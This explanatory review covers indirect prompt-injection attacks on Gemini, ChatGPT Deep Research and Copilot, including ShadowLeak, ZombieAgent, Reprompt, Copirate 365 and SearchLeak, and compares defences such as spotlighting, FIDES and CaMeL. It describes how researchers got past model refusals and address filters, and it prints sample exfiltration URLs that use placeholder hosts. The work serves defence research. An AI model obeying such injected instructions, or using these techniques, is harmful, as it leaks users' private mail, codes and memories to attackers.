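Tenable also found two unusual ways to get instructions into Gemini products. A malicious website could add entries to a visitor's Google search history, which Gemini read to personalise its answers. An attacker could also put instructions in the part of a web request that normally identifies the visitor's browser. A company's cloud service would log them, and Gemini Cloud Assist, which helps people run such services, would read them when an employee asked about the log entry. When Tenable demonstrated this second method, Gemini's summary of the log included a phishing link.

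Tenable used the browsing tool to obtain a user's location and the facts Gemini had saved about them, far less than a mailbox would contain. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* advisory warns that Gemini's connections to other Google services might widen the damage, but does not demonstrate this. Google received the report on 16 April 2025 and fixed the problem by 18 June. Google says only that it now prevents exfiltration through browsing in indirect prompt injections. To address the other two flaws, it stopped showing clickable links in log summaries and withdrew the model version that had followed instructions in the search history.

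### ShadowLeak: a mailbox and a research agent

On the day Google fixed the browsing tool, the security firm Radware reported a similar leak in ChatGPT that could expose much more valuable data. Deep Research is a ChatGPT mode that spends five to thirty minutes reading websites and documents and then writes a report. Users can also connect it to Gmail so it can read their mail. A single agent then has access to a private mailbox, messages from strangers and a tool for opening web pages.

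Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an email that appears to concern a company restructuring. Text that the recipient may not be able to see tells the agent to find an employee's name and home address elsewhere in the inbox, and to look that person up on what purports to be a staff directory. With invented details, the agent would open something like this:

`https://directory.example/lookup/Ines-Moor-8-Quay-Street`

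No directory exists. The attacker runs the server and reads the name and address from its log. The user had asked Deep Research to search the day's emails for information about a new employee, and nothing on the screen showed that the agent had opened the page. The user didn't open the attacker's email or click anything, so the attack fits even the strict definition of zero-click.

The attack on Deep Research was harder than this outline suggests. The agent identified a direct request to send personal data as malicious and blocked it, and several disguised versions failed too. Getting the model to accept the task was easier than getting it to open a suspicious address. Like Tenable, Radware learned the name of the internal browsing tool, partly from the agent's displayed reasoning, and instructions that named the tool worked some of the time. The agent still would not put plain personal details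 in an address. Radware got past this by telling the model to encode them first, supposedly for security, so the software that sent the request handled only a meaningless string.

Radware reports that every repeated test succeeded from then on. These tests used a favourable set-up, in which the mailbox held both the attacker's email and a suitable secret, and the user asked the agent to read every relevant source. Radware didn't measure how often an email to a randomly chosen employee would work. The same method could start from a calendar invitation, a shared file or a chat message, since Deep Research could connect to all of these, but Radware demonstrated it only with Gmail.

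OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August 2025, about seven weeks after the report, without telling Radware, and acknowledged it on 3 September. Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025), a shorter advisory with the same main title, calls the flaw the first zero-click injection in ChatGPT to leak data from the service's own servers. The claim may well be right for ChatGPT, but Tenable's report on Gemini came two months earlier, and Slack's servers had sent data out through link previews in Rehberger's tests that May.

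### What a company's own monitoring can record

Many companies route employees' web traffic through a secure web gateway, a server that inspects and logs it. In ForcedLeak, the employee's browser requested an image directly from the attacker's server. A gateway would have logged that connection, and one that decrypts traffic could also have logged the full image address, which contained the stolen data. The security team might have overlooked one request among many thousands, but an investigator could have found it later.

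With ShadowLeak, the employee's laptop communicates only with ChatGPT. OpenAI's servers collect the mail from Google's servers, and OpenAI's browsing tool sends the request to the attacker, so neither connection passes through the employer's equipment. That equipment can record that the employee used ChatGPT, but an ordinary research task produces the same record.

Infosecurity Magazine's *Zero-Click Vulnerability in ChatGPT's Agent Enables Silent Gmail Data Theft*, like Radware, groups EchoLeak with the earlier browser-side attacks. That is right about how the leak began, but by Ravia's account a Teams server made the final request to the attacker, which puts EchoLeak somewhere in between:

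| | ForcedLeak | EchoLeak | ShadowLeak |
|---|---|---|---|
| What starts the leak | The browser loads an image | The browser loads an image | The agent opens a web page |
| Which computer contacts the attacker | The employee's | A Teams server | An OpenAI server |
| Does the chat page's CSP apply? | Yes, but it listed the expired domain | Yes, but it listed Teams | No |
| What the company's network can record | A connection to the attacker's server | A connection to Teams | A connection to ChatGPT |

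Sending the data from the server also gave the attacker a wider choice of destinations. ChatGPT loaded images only from addresses that passed OpenAI's check, so Zenity had to find a storage service that the check accepted. Radware found no comparable limit on the pages that Deep Research could open.

The useful evidence for a customer is in the vendor's records of which addresses the agent opened and what it had read beforehand. Radware recommends continuously comparing an agent's actions with what the user asked for and blocking those that don't fit, and it was developing a product to do this. The idea is sensible, but the monitor has to run where it can observe the agent's requests. If the agent runs on OpenAI's servers, OpenAI has to run the monitor or give customers access.

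OpenAI has one advantage when the request comes from its own server: it can restrict the request there for every user at once. Its address check for images protected only the apps that called it, and the others kept leaking data.

### ZombieAgent: one address for each letter

After ShadowLeak, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from altering web addresses, even on explicit instruction. It could still open an address exactly as it appeared in an email, but an attacker could no longer supply the first part of an address and have the model add the secret.

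Radware reported a way around this on 26 September 2025. In *ZombieAgent*, the malicious email contains a ready-made web address for every letter and digit, along with instructions that make ChatGPT find a secret and open the addresses that spell it. To send the code 4471, ChatGPT opens the address for 4 twice, then those for 7 and 1. None of these addresses contains the secret, but the attacker can reconstruct it from the sequence of requests.

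Radware also numbered the addresses so that each one stood for a character in a particular position, which let the attacker restore the order. With 26 letters and 10 digits, a block of *b* characters takes 36*b* addresses, or 360 for a block of ten. The method needs one request per character, which is slow for a long contract but quick enough for a password or a customer's name. Rehberger had described the same trick in 2023, when testing which images OpenAI's address check allowed.

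The Ars Technica article *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* compares OpenAI's rule to a new highway guardrail that fits the compact car in the last crash but not larger vehicles. The comparison is a little unfair, since the rule did make theft slower. But the rule only banned constructing new addresses, and an attacker needs only a choice between existing ones to steal data.

The attack could also persist across conversations. OpenAI had tried to keep ChatGPT's long-term memory separate from outside content. Once a chat had used a connector, it could not use the memory, and ChatGPT would not open an attacker's web address stored there. Radware got around both restrictions with a malicious file that the user had to share with ChatGPT once. The file planted a rule in memory to read a certain email before answering any message and to follow the email's instructions. This worked because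 ChatGPT could still use its memory first and Gmail afterwards, and the memory held only a reference to the email, not a web address. A second planted rule made ChatGPT save any sensitive information the user mentioned.

Radware (2026) announced the attack on 8 January and warned of a "worm-like" campaign inside organisations. As Radware describes it, the email makes ChatGPT send out addresses from the victim's inbox, and the attacker's server then emails the same instructions to each of them. The spread is less automatic than "worm" implies, because the new emails come from the attacker's server rather than a colleague's account, and each recipient would need to have connected ChatGPT to a mailbox and then ask it about their mail. KBI Media's *Radware Reveals ZombieAgent Zero-Click Vulnerability Enabling Silent AI Agent Takeover* stresses that, as with ShadowLeak, the theft leaves no logs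 on the employee's device and triggers no alerts in the company's firewalls or gateways.

OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December 2025, 81 days after the report. Radware doesn't describe the repair. OpenAI's current rule, which requires an address to be public already, would exclude pages an attacker had just made for one email. But Embrace The Red points out that anyone with a fair-sized website probably has 36 indexed pages already, one for each letter and digit. With thousands of pages, an attacker could assign a whole word to each and send a sentence in a few requests.

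## Defences: filtering what comes in, blocking what goes out, tracking data between

OpenAI's rule against altered web addresses stopped ShadowLeak but not ZombieAgent, and most earlier fixes were just as specific. Vendors and researchers also work on defences that don't depend on guessing the next attack. These defences can filter or mark incoming text, block the routes by which data could leave, or track where each piece of data came from and limit what the assistant does with it.

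In July 2025, a month after EchoLeak became public, Microsoft (2025) published an account of its layered defences. It distinguishes probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails whatever the model writes. Microsoft prefers deterministic defences where possible. But it calls detecting injected instructions deterministically an open research challenge, so every filter on incoming text remains probabilistic.

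### Marking and screening incoming text

Microsoft offers developers a classifier called Prompt Shields, which does the same job as the XPIA classifier that EchoLeak's email got past. Microsoft trained it on known attack techniques in several languages and keeps updating it. When Prompt Shields flags something, the application has to block the prompt or take some other defensive step.

Another method leaves the hostile text in place but makes its origin more obvious to the model. Hines, Lopez and colleagues (2024), in *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting*, described three versions developed at Microsoft. The simplest puts special marks before and after the outside text. "Datamarking" replaces every space in it with a symbol, so that a line from an email becomes:

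`The^quote^is^valid^until^Friday`

The third version converts the whole text into an encoding such as base64, which capable models can read. In each version, the application's standing instructions explain the change and tell the model not to follow any instructions in the marked text.

The group tested spotlighting on 1,000 artificial documents, each containing a command to reply with a single keyword. When GPT-3.5 Turbo summarised them, datamarking cut the attack success rate from about 50 percent to 3.1 percent, with no measurable loss on four language benchmarks. Encoding did better, but GPT-3.5 Turbo made decoding mistakes, so Hines and colleagues recommended it only for the most capable models. All the attacks were variations on one simple command, so the results are limited evidence of how well spotlighting would work against an attacker who writes an email with it in mind.

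Google has studied a similar technique for Gemini. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes inserting a mark every eight characters into an email's sender, subject and body. The marks worked mainly by breaking the injected words into unfamiliar pieces. This gives less reason to trust the method than if the model had learned whose instructions to follow, and the method will probably work poorly in some languages, according to the paper. Google combines model-level measures with limits on output, such as the restrictions on images and links that Tenable encountered in Gemini.

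A filter can also stop an email before it reaches the mailbox. Microsoft (2026) announced in July that Defender for Office 365, its email security service, would look for injections aimed at AI assistants. *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections* (Office 365 for IT Pros, 2026) reports that the service treats such messages as high-confidence phishing and quarantines them, so Copilot can't retrieve them. The protection is on by default for customers with the more expensive Defender plan or a Microsoft 365 E5 licence, but it covers only email, so an attacker could still use a shared document.

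### A contest against an email assistant

The best public evidence on these filters comes from a contest that Microsoft and academic partners ran between December 2024 and April 2025. *LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) reports that 839 participants made 461,640 attempts to hijack a simulated email assistant. Each attempt was one email, which succeeded if the assistant used its email-sending tool as the attacker wanted.

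One of the four settings resembled EchoLeak. A user asked about the second-quarter budget, and the search returned the ten most relevant emails. The attacker's message had to be among them, get past the defence, and make the assistant send out a profit forecast from another email. Participants knew which defence they faced and learned which steps each attempt had completed, but they couldn't see the assistant's answer.

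In the first phase, about 3,000 of 371,000 submissions (less than 1 percent) completed every step. Evading detection also seemed to make an email less effective. Of the emails the defences detected, 19 percent made the model call the tool, compared with 4 percent of those they missed.

A low success rate per email is less reassuring when the attacker can keep trying, so the organisers also counted how many teams eventually succeeded. The table gives the share of teams that did so in the budget setting, with OpenAI's GPT-4o mini as the assistant. The last column gives the average number of failed attempts before a team's first success, across all four settings.

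| Defence | Teams that eventually succeeded | Attempts before first success |
|---|---|---|
| Prompt Shields, a text classifier | 60% | 89 |
| Spotlighting | 53% | Not reported |
| TaskTracker, which reads the model's internal activity | 44% | 159 |
| A second language model as judge | 32% | 506 |
| All of them together | 17% | Not reported |

The organisers then reran the detectors on the first-phase emails that had triggered the tool, using settings that raised no false alarms on their harmless test emails. Two versions of the text classifier caught 60 and 68 percent of these emails, but only 43 and 49 percent of the second phase's attacks. The language-model judge caught 99.4 percent in the first phase and 96.5 percent in the second, but it is much more expensive to run.

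Text classifiers struggled because many of the attacks, like EchoLeak's email, looked like ordinary work mail. One successful submission read like a message from a stressed colleague, asking for a forgotten confirmation to be sent and offering pizza and beer in return. Abdelnabi and colleagues suggest that a better detector would check whether the sender is addressing the user or the assistant, and whether the user asked for the proposed action.

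In the second phase, nobody got past the full set of defences protecting GPT-4o mini. This is good evidence for using several filters together, although that phase was shorter and had fewer participants. The organisers also changed several defences at once, so they couldn't tell which changes had helped.

Results were much less encouraging in a broader test by Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), *The Attacker Moves Second*. They tried to break 12 published defences, including spotlighting, against prompt injection and jailbreaks (attempts by users to get around a model's rules). They adapted their attacks to each defence and succeeded more than 90 percent of the time against most of them, whereas the original papers had mostly reported attack success rates near zero.

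False alarms are the main drawback of stricter filtering. During the contest, the organisers kept each classifier's false-alarm rate below 5 percent on their test data. At a rate just under that limit, an employee who receives 100 harmless emails a day could lose nearly five of them.

### Blocking the exits

Microsoft cites its response to Rehberger's report of the image leak as an example of deterministic blocking. The company says it also looked for variants and took similar steps against some untrusted links.

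EchoLeak, which Microsoft has since fixed, got past both a link filter and a Content Security Policy (CSP). Deterministic defences like these guarantee only that their own rules are enforced. Both controls worked as specified, but their rules didn't cover every way data could leave.

Blocking the routes data can leave by also removes useful links and images. OpenAI's check for addresses that are already public preserves some of them, but it interrupts users when an address is new. Some websites ask OpenAI not to catalogue them, so ChatGPT asks for confirmation before opening any link to them.

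A request may also contain personal information that the user is happy to send. A help page from OpenAI gives the example of a car search link that includes the user's home city, London. The search needs this information to be useful, so ChatGPT may ask the user to approve the link. OpenAI claims only that the address check prevents the agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address. The check doesn't establish that the page is trustworthy or free of injected instructions.

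Approval works best when the user can see exactly what will leave and where it will go. Microsoft gives the example of Copilot in Outlook, which can draft an email but leaves the user to send it. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) warn of confirmation fatigue, in which people who see too many requests begin approving them without thinking. Approval also does little good if the user can't recognise the data, as with the invisible characters in Rehberger's 2024 attack on Copilot.

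An assistant's tools can leak data in ways that a filter on images and links doesn't block. Microsoft describes an assistant that can write to a public code repository, where anyone could read what it posts. It also describes a much narrower channel, in which an outsider can observe whether the assistant used a certain tool. An injection can then leak one bit of information by making the assistant use the tool or not, depending on that bit's value.

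OpenAI's Lockdown Mode blocks many routes for data exfiltration at once. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) presented it in February as an optional setting for people at higher risk, such as executives and security staff. OpenAI at first offered it only on plans for organisations, then began extending it to personal accounts in June. With the setting on, ChatGPT browses only stored copies of web pages, so browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent both depended on such requests.

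In exchange for protection, Lockdown Mode switches off Deep Research and agent mode, stops ChatGPT from downloading files, and limits images in its answers. Search results may also be out of date or missing. OpenAI says most users don't need the mode.

OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* describes risks that remain when the feature is on. OpenAI doesn't guarantee that it stops all data from getting out, and an injection in a stored web page or an uploaded file can still distort an answer. In company-managed workspaces, the setting doesn't automatically disable every connected app, so administrators must choose which apps and actions to allow. OpenAI advises against any action that changes something an attacker might be able to see. Lockdown Mode also leaves network access unchanged in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Users with personal accounts can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat.

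### Labels for trust and secrecy

Lockdown Mode restricts outside requests even when no private data is involved. Information-flow control instead labels data by trust and secrecy, and blocks only actions that would mix the labels unsafely. An assistant can therefore have all three parts of the lethal trifecta without combining them in one dangerous action.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, developed a system of this kind at Microsoft, called FIDES. Every item gets two labels. The integrity label records whether the item is trusted or untrusted, and the confidentiality label can list the people allowed to read it. If the assistant produces something from items *x* and *y*, the result is untrusted if either item was untrusted. Its permitted readers are those who could read both:

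readers(*x* and *y*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

Before the assistant uses a tool, ordinary software outside the model checks the labels against a policy. FIDES has two basic rules:

- **Trusted action:** the assistant may take a consequential action only if it made the decision, and chose the details that matter, without influence from untrusted data.
- **Permitted flow:** the assistant may send data only if every recipient is allowed to read it.

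A policy can require one rule or both, depending on the tool. In the later work by Kolluri and colleagues, a tool that sends data out must satisfy at least one.

Suppose Ana, a purchasing manager, asks an assistant to compare a supplier's emailed quote with a confidential budget file. Ben, a colleague, also has access to the file. The email contains an instruction to look up the quote at this address, with the budget limit attached:

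`https://check.example/quote?limit=48000`

The labels are as follows:

| Item | Trusted? | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| Ana's request | Yes | Anyone |
| The supplier's email | No | Ana and the supplier |
| The budget file | Yes | Ana and Ben |
| Anything the assistant writes from all three | No | Ana |

If the model follows the instruction and tries to open the address, the request fails the trusted-action rule because the model made it after reading an untrusted email. It also fails the permitted-flow rule because the unknown owner of check.example isn't allowed to read the budget. The software blocks the request without recognising the email as an attack, so rewording the email doesn't help the attacker.

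But these labels would also block legitimate work. If Ana asked the assistant to send the comparison to Ben, a simple version of the system would refuse because the assistant has read an untrusted email and Ben wasn't a recipient of it. FIDES avoids this by hiding untrusted text from the model that plans the work. The planning model sees only a variable, a name that stands for the email's contents. A second model, which has no tools, reads the contents and writes the comparison into another variable. The planning model then sends that variable to Ben without reading it. The decision to send it came entirely from Ana's request, so the action counts as trusted.

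Willison proposed this division between two models in 2023. It protects the decision to send the comparison but not the comparison's accuracy, since the supplier's email could still make the second model wrongly report that the quote is within budget.

As Costa and colleagues tested it, FIDES would also need a change to stop an image leak like EchoLeak. It checked tool calls but treated the answer to the user as harmless, and EchoLeak's image was in the answer. The paper notes that FIDES can apply its policies to answers too. An assistant whose chat window loads images or links would need this.

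The guarantee also covers only data that passes directly into an action. An outsider who can see which tools the assistant uses, and in what order, may still infer something about the data. ZombieAgent's server similarly recovered a secret from a sequence of harmless addresses. The trusted-action rule blocks ZombieAgent's method because the addresses came from the malicious email.

### How many tasks the rules cost

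Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks, some with injections in the data. With GPT-4o as the model, they measured how many tasks each agent completed without attacks, then counted successful attacks, excluding cases the benchmark had misjudged.

| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
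| Ordinary agent, no rules | 75% | 70% | 99% | 93% | 152 |
| Ordinary agent with rules | 37% | 73% | 38% | 20% | 0 |
| FIDES, rules switched off | 64% | 50% | 65% | 64% | 21 |
| FIDES with rules | 59% | 41% | 53% | 48% | 0 |

The rules stopped every attack, with or without hidden variables. This was almost inevitable, because the researchers had labelled a field untrusted whenever any attack in the benchmark used it. A company would have to choose its labels without knowing which fields the next attack will use. If it trusted everything employees wrote, the rules would not stop an attack like the one on Slack AI, where the attacker had an account in the workspace.

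Averaged over the four areas, task completion fell from about 84 percent for the ordinary agent to 50 percent for FIDES with its rules. Some of this loss came from GPT-4o confusing variable names or reading untrusted data unnecessarily. A stronger reasoning model, OpenAI's o1, raised completion on the travel tasks from 41 to 68 percent.

The rules themselves cause other losses. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which may include scheduling a payment. Once the agent reads an untrusted file, the policy blocks the payment. It blocks payment of honest bills too, because the software cannot distinguish them from fraudulent ones with the same labels.

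Kolluri and colleagues, also at Microsoft, argue that this comparison makes the rules look worse than they are. To be safe, an agent without labels usually has to ask for approval before every consequential action, whereas FIDES needs to ask only when an action breaks a rule. In their tests with OpenAI's o3-mini model, the agent without labels needed about 48 approvals across the benchmark and FIDES needed 19, counting only the tasks that each agent completed.

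Their own system, Prudentia, tells the model about the rules so it can plan around them. With no approvals, it completed 59 percent of tasks, compared with 50 percent for FIDES and 24 percent for the ordinary agent. Prudentia can also ask the user to vouch for a piece of untrusted data. If a colleague emails a list of ten jobs, the user can approve the email once instead of ten separate actions. But if the user approves a malicious email, the assistant treats every instruction in it as trusted.

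### CaMeL: planning before reading

Google DeepMind's CaMeL (2025) makes the assistant plan its steps before it reads anything from outside. One model receives the user's request and a description of the available tools, and writes a short program that lists the steps. When the program needs information from emails or other outside text, a second model, which has no tools, extracts it. Separate software runs the program, tracks where each value came from and checks security policies before each tool call.

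For Ana's request, the program would fetch the email, open the budget file, have the second model compare them and show the result. The email can't add a step that opens check.example, because the first model wrote the program without reading the email. The program may take one action if the quote is within budget and another if it isn't, so the email can influence which action it takes.

An attacker can still tamper with data the plan uses. If Ana asked the assistant to send a document to the address in an email, the attacker could change the address without changing the plan. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) explains that CaMeL's policies cover this case by checking whether the data may go to that recipient. The paper also states that CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo with comparable task performance.

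More recent tests found a larger drawback. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested CaMeL with five models in systems where one agent delegates to several others. They switched off the extra policies, leaving only the separation between planning and reading. Across 949 attack cases per model, the average attack success rate fell from 12.9 percent to 0.2 percent. For GPT-4.1, the most vulnerable model, it fell from 36.1 percent to 0.5 percent.

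The remaining attacks worked because one agent could include outside text in its instructions to another, which then treated that text as trusted. Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by making agents pass outside text separately from instructions, and no attack in the test succeeded after that.

On a separate benchmark of 112 professional tasks, CaMeL lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points. The drop was 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Closing the gap between agents lowered the rate by another 3.2 points on average, but by less than one point for those two. A model using CaMeL has to write the program that handles a tool's output before seeing any of that output, and better models can do this more reliably. The researchers also had to add an exact description of each tool's output format, which a company could prepare once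 for its own tools.

### Can better models and filters be enough?

OpenAI is among the companies more optimistic about training models to resist prompt injection. *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that most attacks the company knows of against ChatGPT fail because safety training makes the model refuse. OpenAI expects a "maximally intelligent" model to resist manipulation better than a human would. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an automated attacker, trained through reinforcement learning, that looks for weaknesses in the Atlas browser's agent so that the company can fix them first.

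But OpenAI doesn't propose relying on training alone. In the same March 2026 post, it says filters usually miss well-developed attacks, because detecting them is as hard as detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. It recommends limiting what a manipulated agent can do, as a shop limits the refunds an employee can give. In its guidance, Microsoft goes further and tells developers to assume injection is inevitable. Kolluri and colleagues argue that systems handling critical work need deterministic limits because probabilistic defences offer no guarantee.

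The best models have become quite hard to hijack. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a public contest in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 leading models. Some attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5 percent for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 percent for Gemini 2.5 Pro. In the tests by Peters-Gill and colleagues, GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks even without CaMeL.

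Such low rates may still be too high for a company's mailboxes. If each email has an independent chance *p* of success, the chance that at least one of *n* emails succeeds is

1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*

With *p* at 0.5 percent, this gives 63 percent for 200 emails and more than 99 percent for 1,000. These figures are rough, because copies of one email aren't independent trials and the contestants had advantages that a stranger usually lacks, such as seeing the earlier conversation. But successes in the contest kept growing roughly in line with the number of attempts, so the participants weren't running out of ideas.

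Scores on fixed benchmarks can also overstate how well training protects a model. GPT-5 had an attack success rate of at most 0.2 percent on several agent benchmarks. When Abdelnabi and colleagues replayed successful emails from their contest against GPT-5, the rate was 22.8 percent, even though people had written those emails to defeat other models. Peters-Gill and colleagues also caution that GPT-5.5's perfect score may reflect the attacks in the benchmark. In the same tests, Claude Fable 5 refused 52 of 97 harmless tasks, possibly because it associated the benchmark with attacks. Refusing this often would make an agent less useful.

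A vendor can repair a fixed rule more reliably than a trained model. If the rule misses a case, the vendor can find that case and close it for every user. The vendor can also train a model on an attack that got through, but can't know which other wordings would still work. Those who favour training can reply that supposedly firm limits failed in EchoLeak too, and that companies are less likely to use limits that block a third of the assistant's work.

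For data theft, the case for limits is stronger, because an attacker can easily send many emails and needs only one to work. Training and filters are still useful against harms that exit controls can't prevent, such as a false summary. The results for FIDES and CaMeL suggest that better models also make the limits more practical.

### What a customer can change

A company that buys an assistant usually can't edit the vendor's CSP or rebuild its planning system, but it can limit what a successful injection could reach. Copilot works with the employee's permissions, so removing access to folders the employee no longer needs also keeps an attacker from reaching them through Copilot. This works even if nobody detects the attack, and it has few drawbacks if the company chooses the permissions well.

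Microsoft also points customers to sensitivity labels, which mark documents with levels such as "confidential". A company can use a data loss prevention policy in Purview, Microsoft's data governance service, to stop Copilot from summarising files with certain labels. If Ana's budget file had such a label, the attacker couldn't use an email to obtain its contents through a summary, but Ana couldn't have Copilot summarise it either. The company has to label its files and decide which are sensitive enough to justify the inconvenience.

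Setting Copilot to ignore outside email would have stopped EchoLeak, and might suit a legal or finance team that mostly asks about internal records. The setting wouldn't block a malicious file that an employee downloads and saves in a company folder, because Copilot would then find it among internal documents.

In ChatGPT workspaces, administrators can assign Lockdown Mode to particular people or groups and choose which apps and app actions they may use. OpenAI considers reading from a trusted app less risky than writing to it, but a secret read from one app can still leave through another. Eligible customers can also review app activity records through OpenAI's compliance service, which gives them some evidence about requests that never cross their own network.

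## 2026: Microsoft's Copilot assistants leak again

In May 2025, Microsoft blocked the route EchoLeak used to take data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. During 2026, researchers published several other routes, as well as attacks on Copilot Personal, Microsoft's separate assistant for consumers. The two products share some weaknesses but expose different data to an attacker. Copilot Personal has access to what one user has told it and to any accounts that user has connected, while Microsoft 365 Copilot can search an employer's mail and files.

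### Reprompt: a link that asks the question

Many chatbots accept a question as part of a web address. An address like this one opens the chatbot, fills in the question and submits it, just as if the user had typed it:

`https://assistant.example/?q=When+is+the+next+full+moon`

The feature is convenient for bookmarks and links from other programs, but it lets whoever writes a link choose the question. Researchers had already pointed out this risk in ChatGPT and the AI search engine Perplexity before the security firm Varonis exploited the feature in Copilot Personal.

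Varonis' *Reprompt*, published in January 2026, describes an attack that starts when a user clicks a link to Microsoft's real Copilot site. A prompt in the link tells Copilot to add a fact about the user to a web address and open it. Copilot does this with its own web access, so the attack doesn't need an image to load in the chat window. Gemini's browsing tool and ChatGPT's Deep Research had leaked data in much the same way in 2025.

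Copilot had two safeguards against this. It usually refused to open an address without a good reason, and it could remove sensitive details from an address before opening it. Varonis got past the first safeguard by presenting the task as harmless. The second covered only the first request to an address. In a test with an invented secret phrase, Copilot removed the phrase from the first request but sent it intact when it repeated the request. Varonis suspected that Microsoft had limited the check to keep Copilot fast.

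When Copilot opened the address, the attacker's server could reply with another instruction, which requested a new fact and supplied a new address to put it in. In the demonstration, the server requested the user's local time, then their location, then whatever Copilot had learned about them, and finally a summary of their last conversation. Each instruction could depend on the previous answer, so the original link didn't show what the attacker would steal. The exchange continued even if the victim closed the Copilot tab.

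An attacker could take only what Copilot Personal had access to, so Varonis's claim that there was no limit to the amount or type of data is too broad. The demonstration obtained personal details and conversation summaries, which can be very sensitive, but no company files.

The firm also calls Reprompt fundamentally different from EchoLeak because the victim didn't have to type a question, though Reprompt's victim did have to click a link, which EchoLeak's did not. A more important difference is where the attacker's text entered. EchoLeak's instructions were in an email, which an assistant can at least label as outside content. Reprompt's first instructions arrived where the user's own question normally goes, so a defence such as spotlighting, which marks outside text, would not have marked them.

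Microsoft had fixed the flaw by the time Varonis published it. Varonis told companies that Reprompt did not affect Microsoft 365 Copilot, which was true of the attack as a whole, but five months later it showed that a link could put instructions into that product too.

### Copirate 365: a leak through fonts

In March 2026, Microsoft finished fixing a leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot that Rehberger had reported on 16 October 2025. The attack, which Rehberger called Copirate 365, used a new feature that let Copilot write a small web page and preview it in the chat.

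Microsoft removed ordinary images from these previews but left style sheets, which control a page's appearance. A style sheet can also make the browser load outside files, such as a background picture or a font, and the address of each request can carry data.

Copilot's Content Security Policy (CSP) still limited where those requests could go. Rehberger reported on Embrace The Red that the policy varied with the program Copilot was running in, such as SharePoint or Excel for the web. The lists of allowed domains included test environments, and some entries contained what looked like individual employees' usernames. Rehberger took this as a sign that nobody controlled the lists tightly. The rules for fonts were looser still and let the browser contact his own server.

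In one demonstration, instructions in a shared Word document made Copilot find an email, put its text in the address of a font and open the preview, which normally stayed hidden until the user selected it. This is the "hi there" case mentioned earlier, which falls just short of the strict definition of zero-click.

Rehberger also combined the leak with Copilot's long-term memory, which Microsoft had turned on by default for organisations. A document that looked like a biography of Albert Einstein planted a memory when the user replied to a question at the end of Copilot's summary. From then on, whenever the user pasted a password or code into a new conversation, Copilot sent it out in a font address. ChatGPT's macOS app had leaked conversations through planted memories in 2024.

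Microsoft reported fixing this persistent version on 6 December 2025, three months before it closed the font route. But according to its documentation in April 2026, changes to Copilot's memory were still not recorded in the audit log that companies use. A security team that found a planted memory would therefore have struggled to tell when it appeared or which document had caused it.

Rehberger found related problems in the consumer Copilot and reported them separately. One involved the Copilot built into the Edge browser, which could open web pages by itself. An uploaded file could make it visit a web address containing everything stored in its memory about the user. When Rehberger retried the attack a few weeks before presenting it, Copilot consistently blocked the file. He thought Microsoft had probably added filters on incoming text, which would leave the browser tool unchanged.

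Microsoft fixed more flaws in Microsoft 365 Copilot and Copilot Chat in Edge in the spring. VPN Central's *Microsoft Fixes Critical Copilot Flaws That Could Expose Sensitive Data* lists three that Microsoft disclosed on 7 May. Each could have let an outsider obtain sensitive information over a network.

### SearchLeak: an image that loaded too soon

Varonis disclosed another attack on 15 June. It targeted Enterprise Search, the part of Microsoft 365 Copilot that searches a company's mail, meetings and files. *SearchLeak* (2026) explains how the firm combined three weaknesses to steal data with one click. The Next Web reports that Microsoft credited the discovery to Dolev Taler, a researcher at Varonis.

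The attack began with a link, as Reprompt had. Enterprise Search accepted queries in its web address, a feature Microsoft intended for ordinary searches such as "travel policy". Copilot also followed any instructions in the query as soon as the page opened. Varonis had expected stronger safeguards in a product for companies. The Hacker News (2026) pointed out that anti-phishing tools were unlikely to flag the link, because it led to a real Microsoft site.

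Suppose the latest email in the victim's mailbox has the subject line "Your sign-in code is 830614". The attacker's link tells Copilot to find that email and put the code in the address of an image. Copilot then writes an answer in HTML that includes the image.

Microsoft had prepared for this by having its software put Copilot's finished answer inside a code block, which makes a browser display HTML as text instead of acting on it. An image tag inside the block appears as code, and the browser doesn't request the image.

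But Copilot's answers appear on the screen piece by piece as the model writes them, and the software added the code block only at the end. The page therefore briefly contained a working image, which the browser requested immediately. The code block then turned the image into harmless text, but the browser had already sent the request. Programmers call this a race condition because the outcome depends on which of two events happens first.

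The attack exposed a conflict between speed and safety, much like the one Rehberger had suspected behind OpenAI's image check. Software that waits for a complete answer before cleaning it must either hide the answer until then or let the browser act on the unfinished version. Varonis recommends cleaning each piece as the browser displays it. This is harder to program, since a link or image may arrive in several fragments that look harmless separately.

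The browser's request still had to satisfy the CSP. The policy would have blocked the attacker's own server, but it allowed every address under bing.com. Bing can look for pictures that resemble one the user already has. The user gives Bing the address of that picture, and a Bing server fetches it for analysis. With placeholder domains, the image address in Copilot's answer looked roughly like this:

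`https://search.example/similar?picture=pictures.example/830614.png`

Here search.example stands for Bing. The browser sends its request there, which the policy permits. Bing's server then requests the file from pictures.example, and the attacker reads 830614 in the log. *EchoLeak* had described the same kind of proxy fetch in Teams the year before.

The victim might have noticed Copilot "thinking" about a question they had never asked and then giving a strange answer, but by then the code was on the attacker's server.

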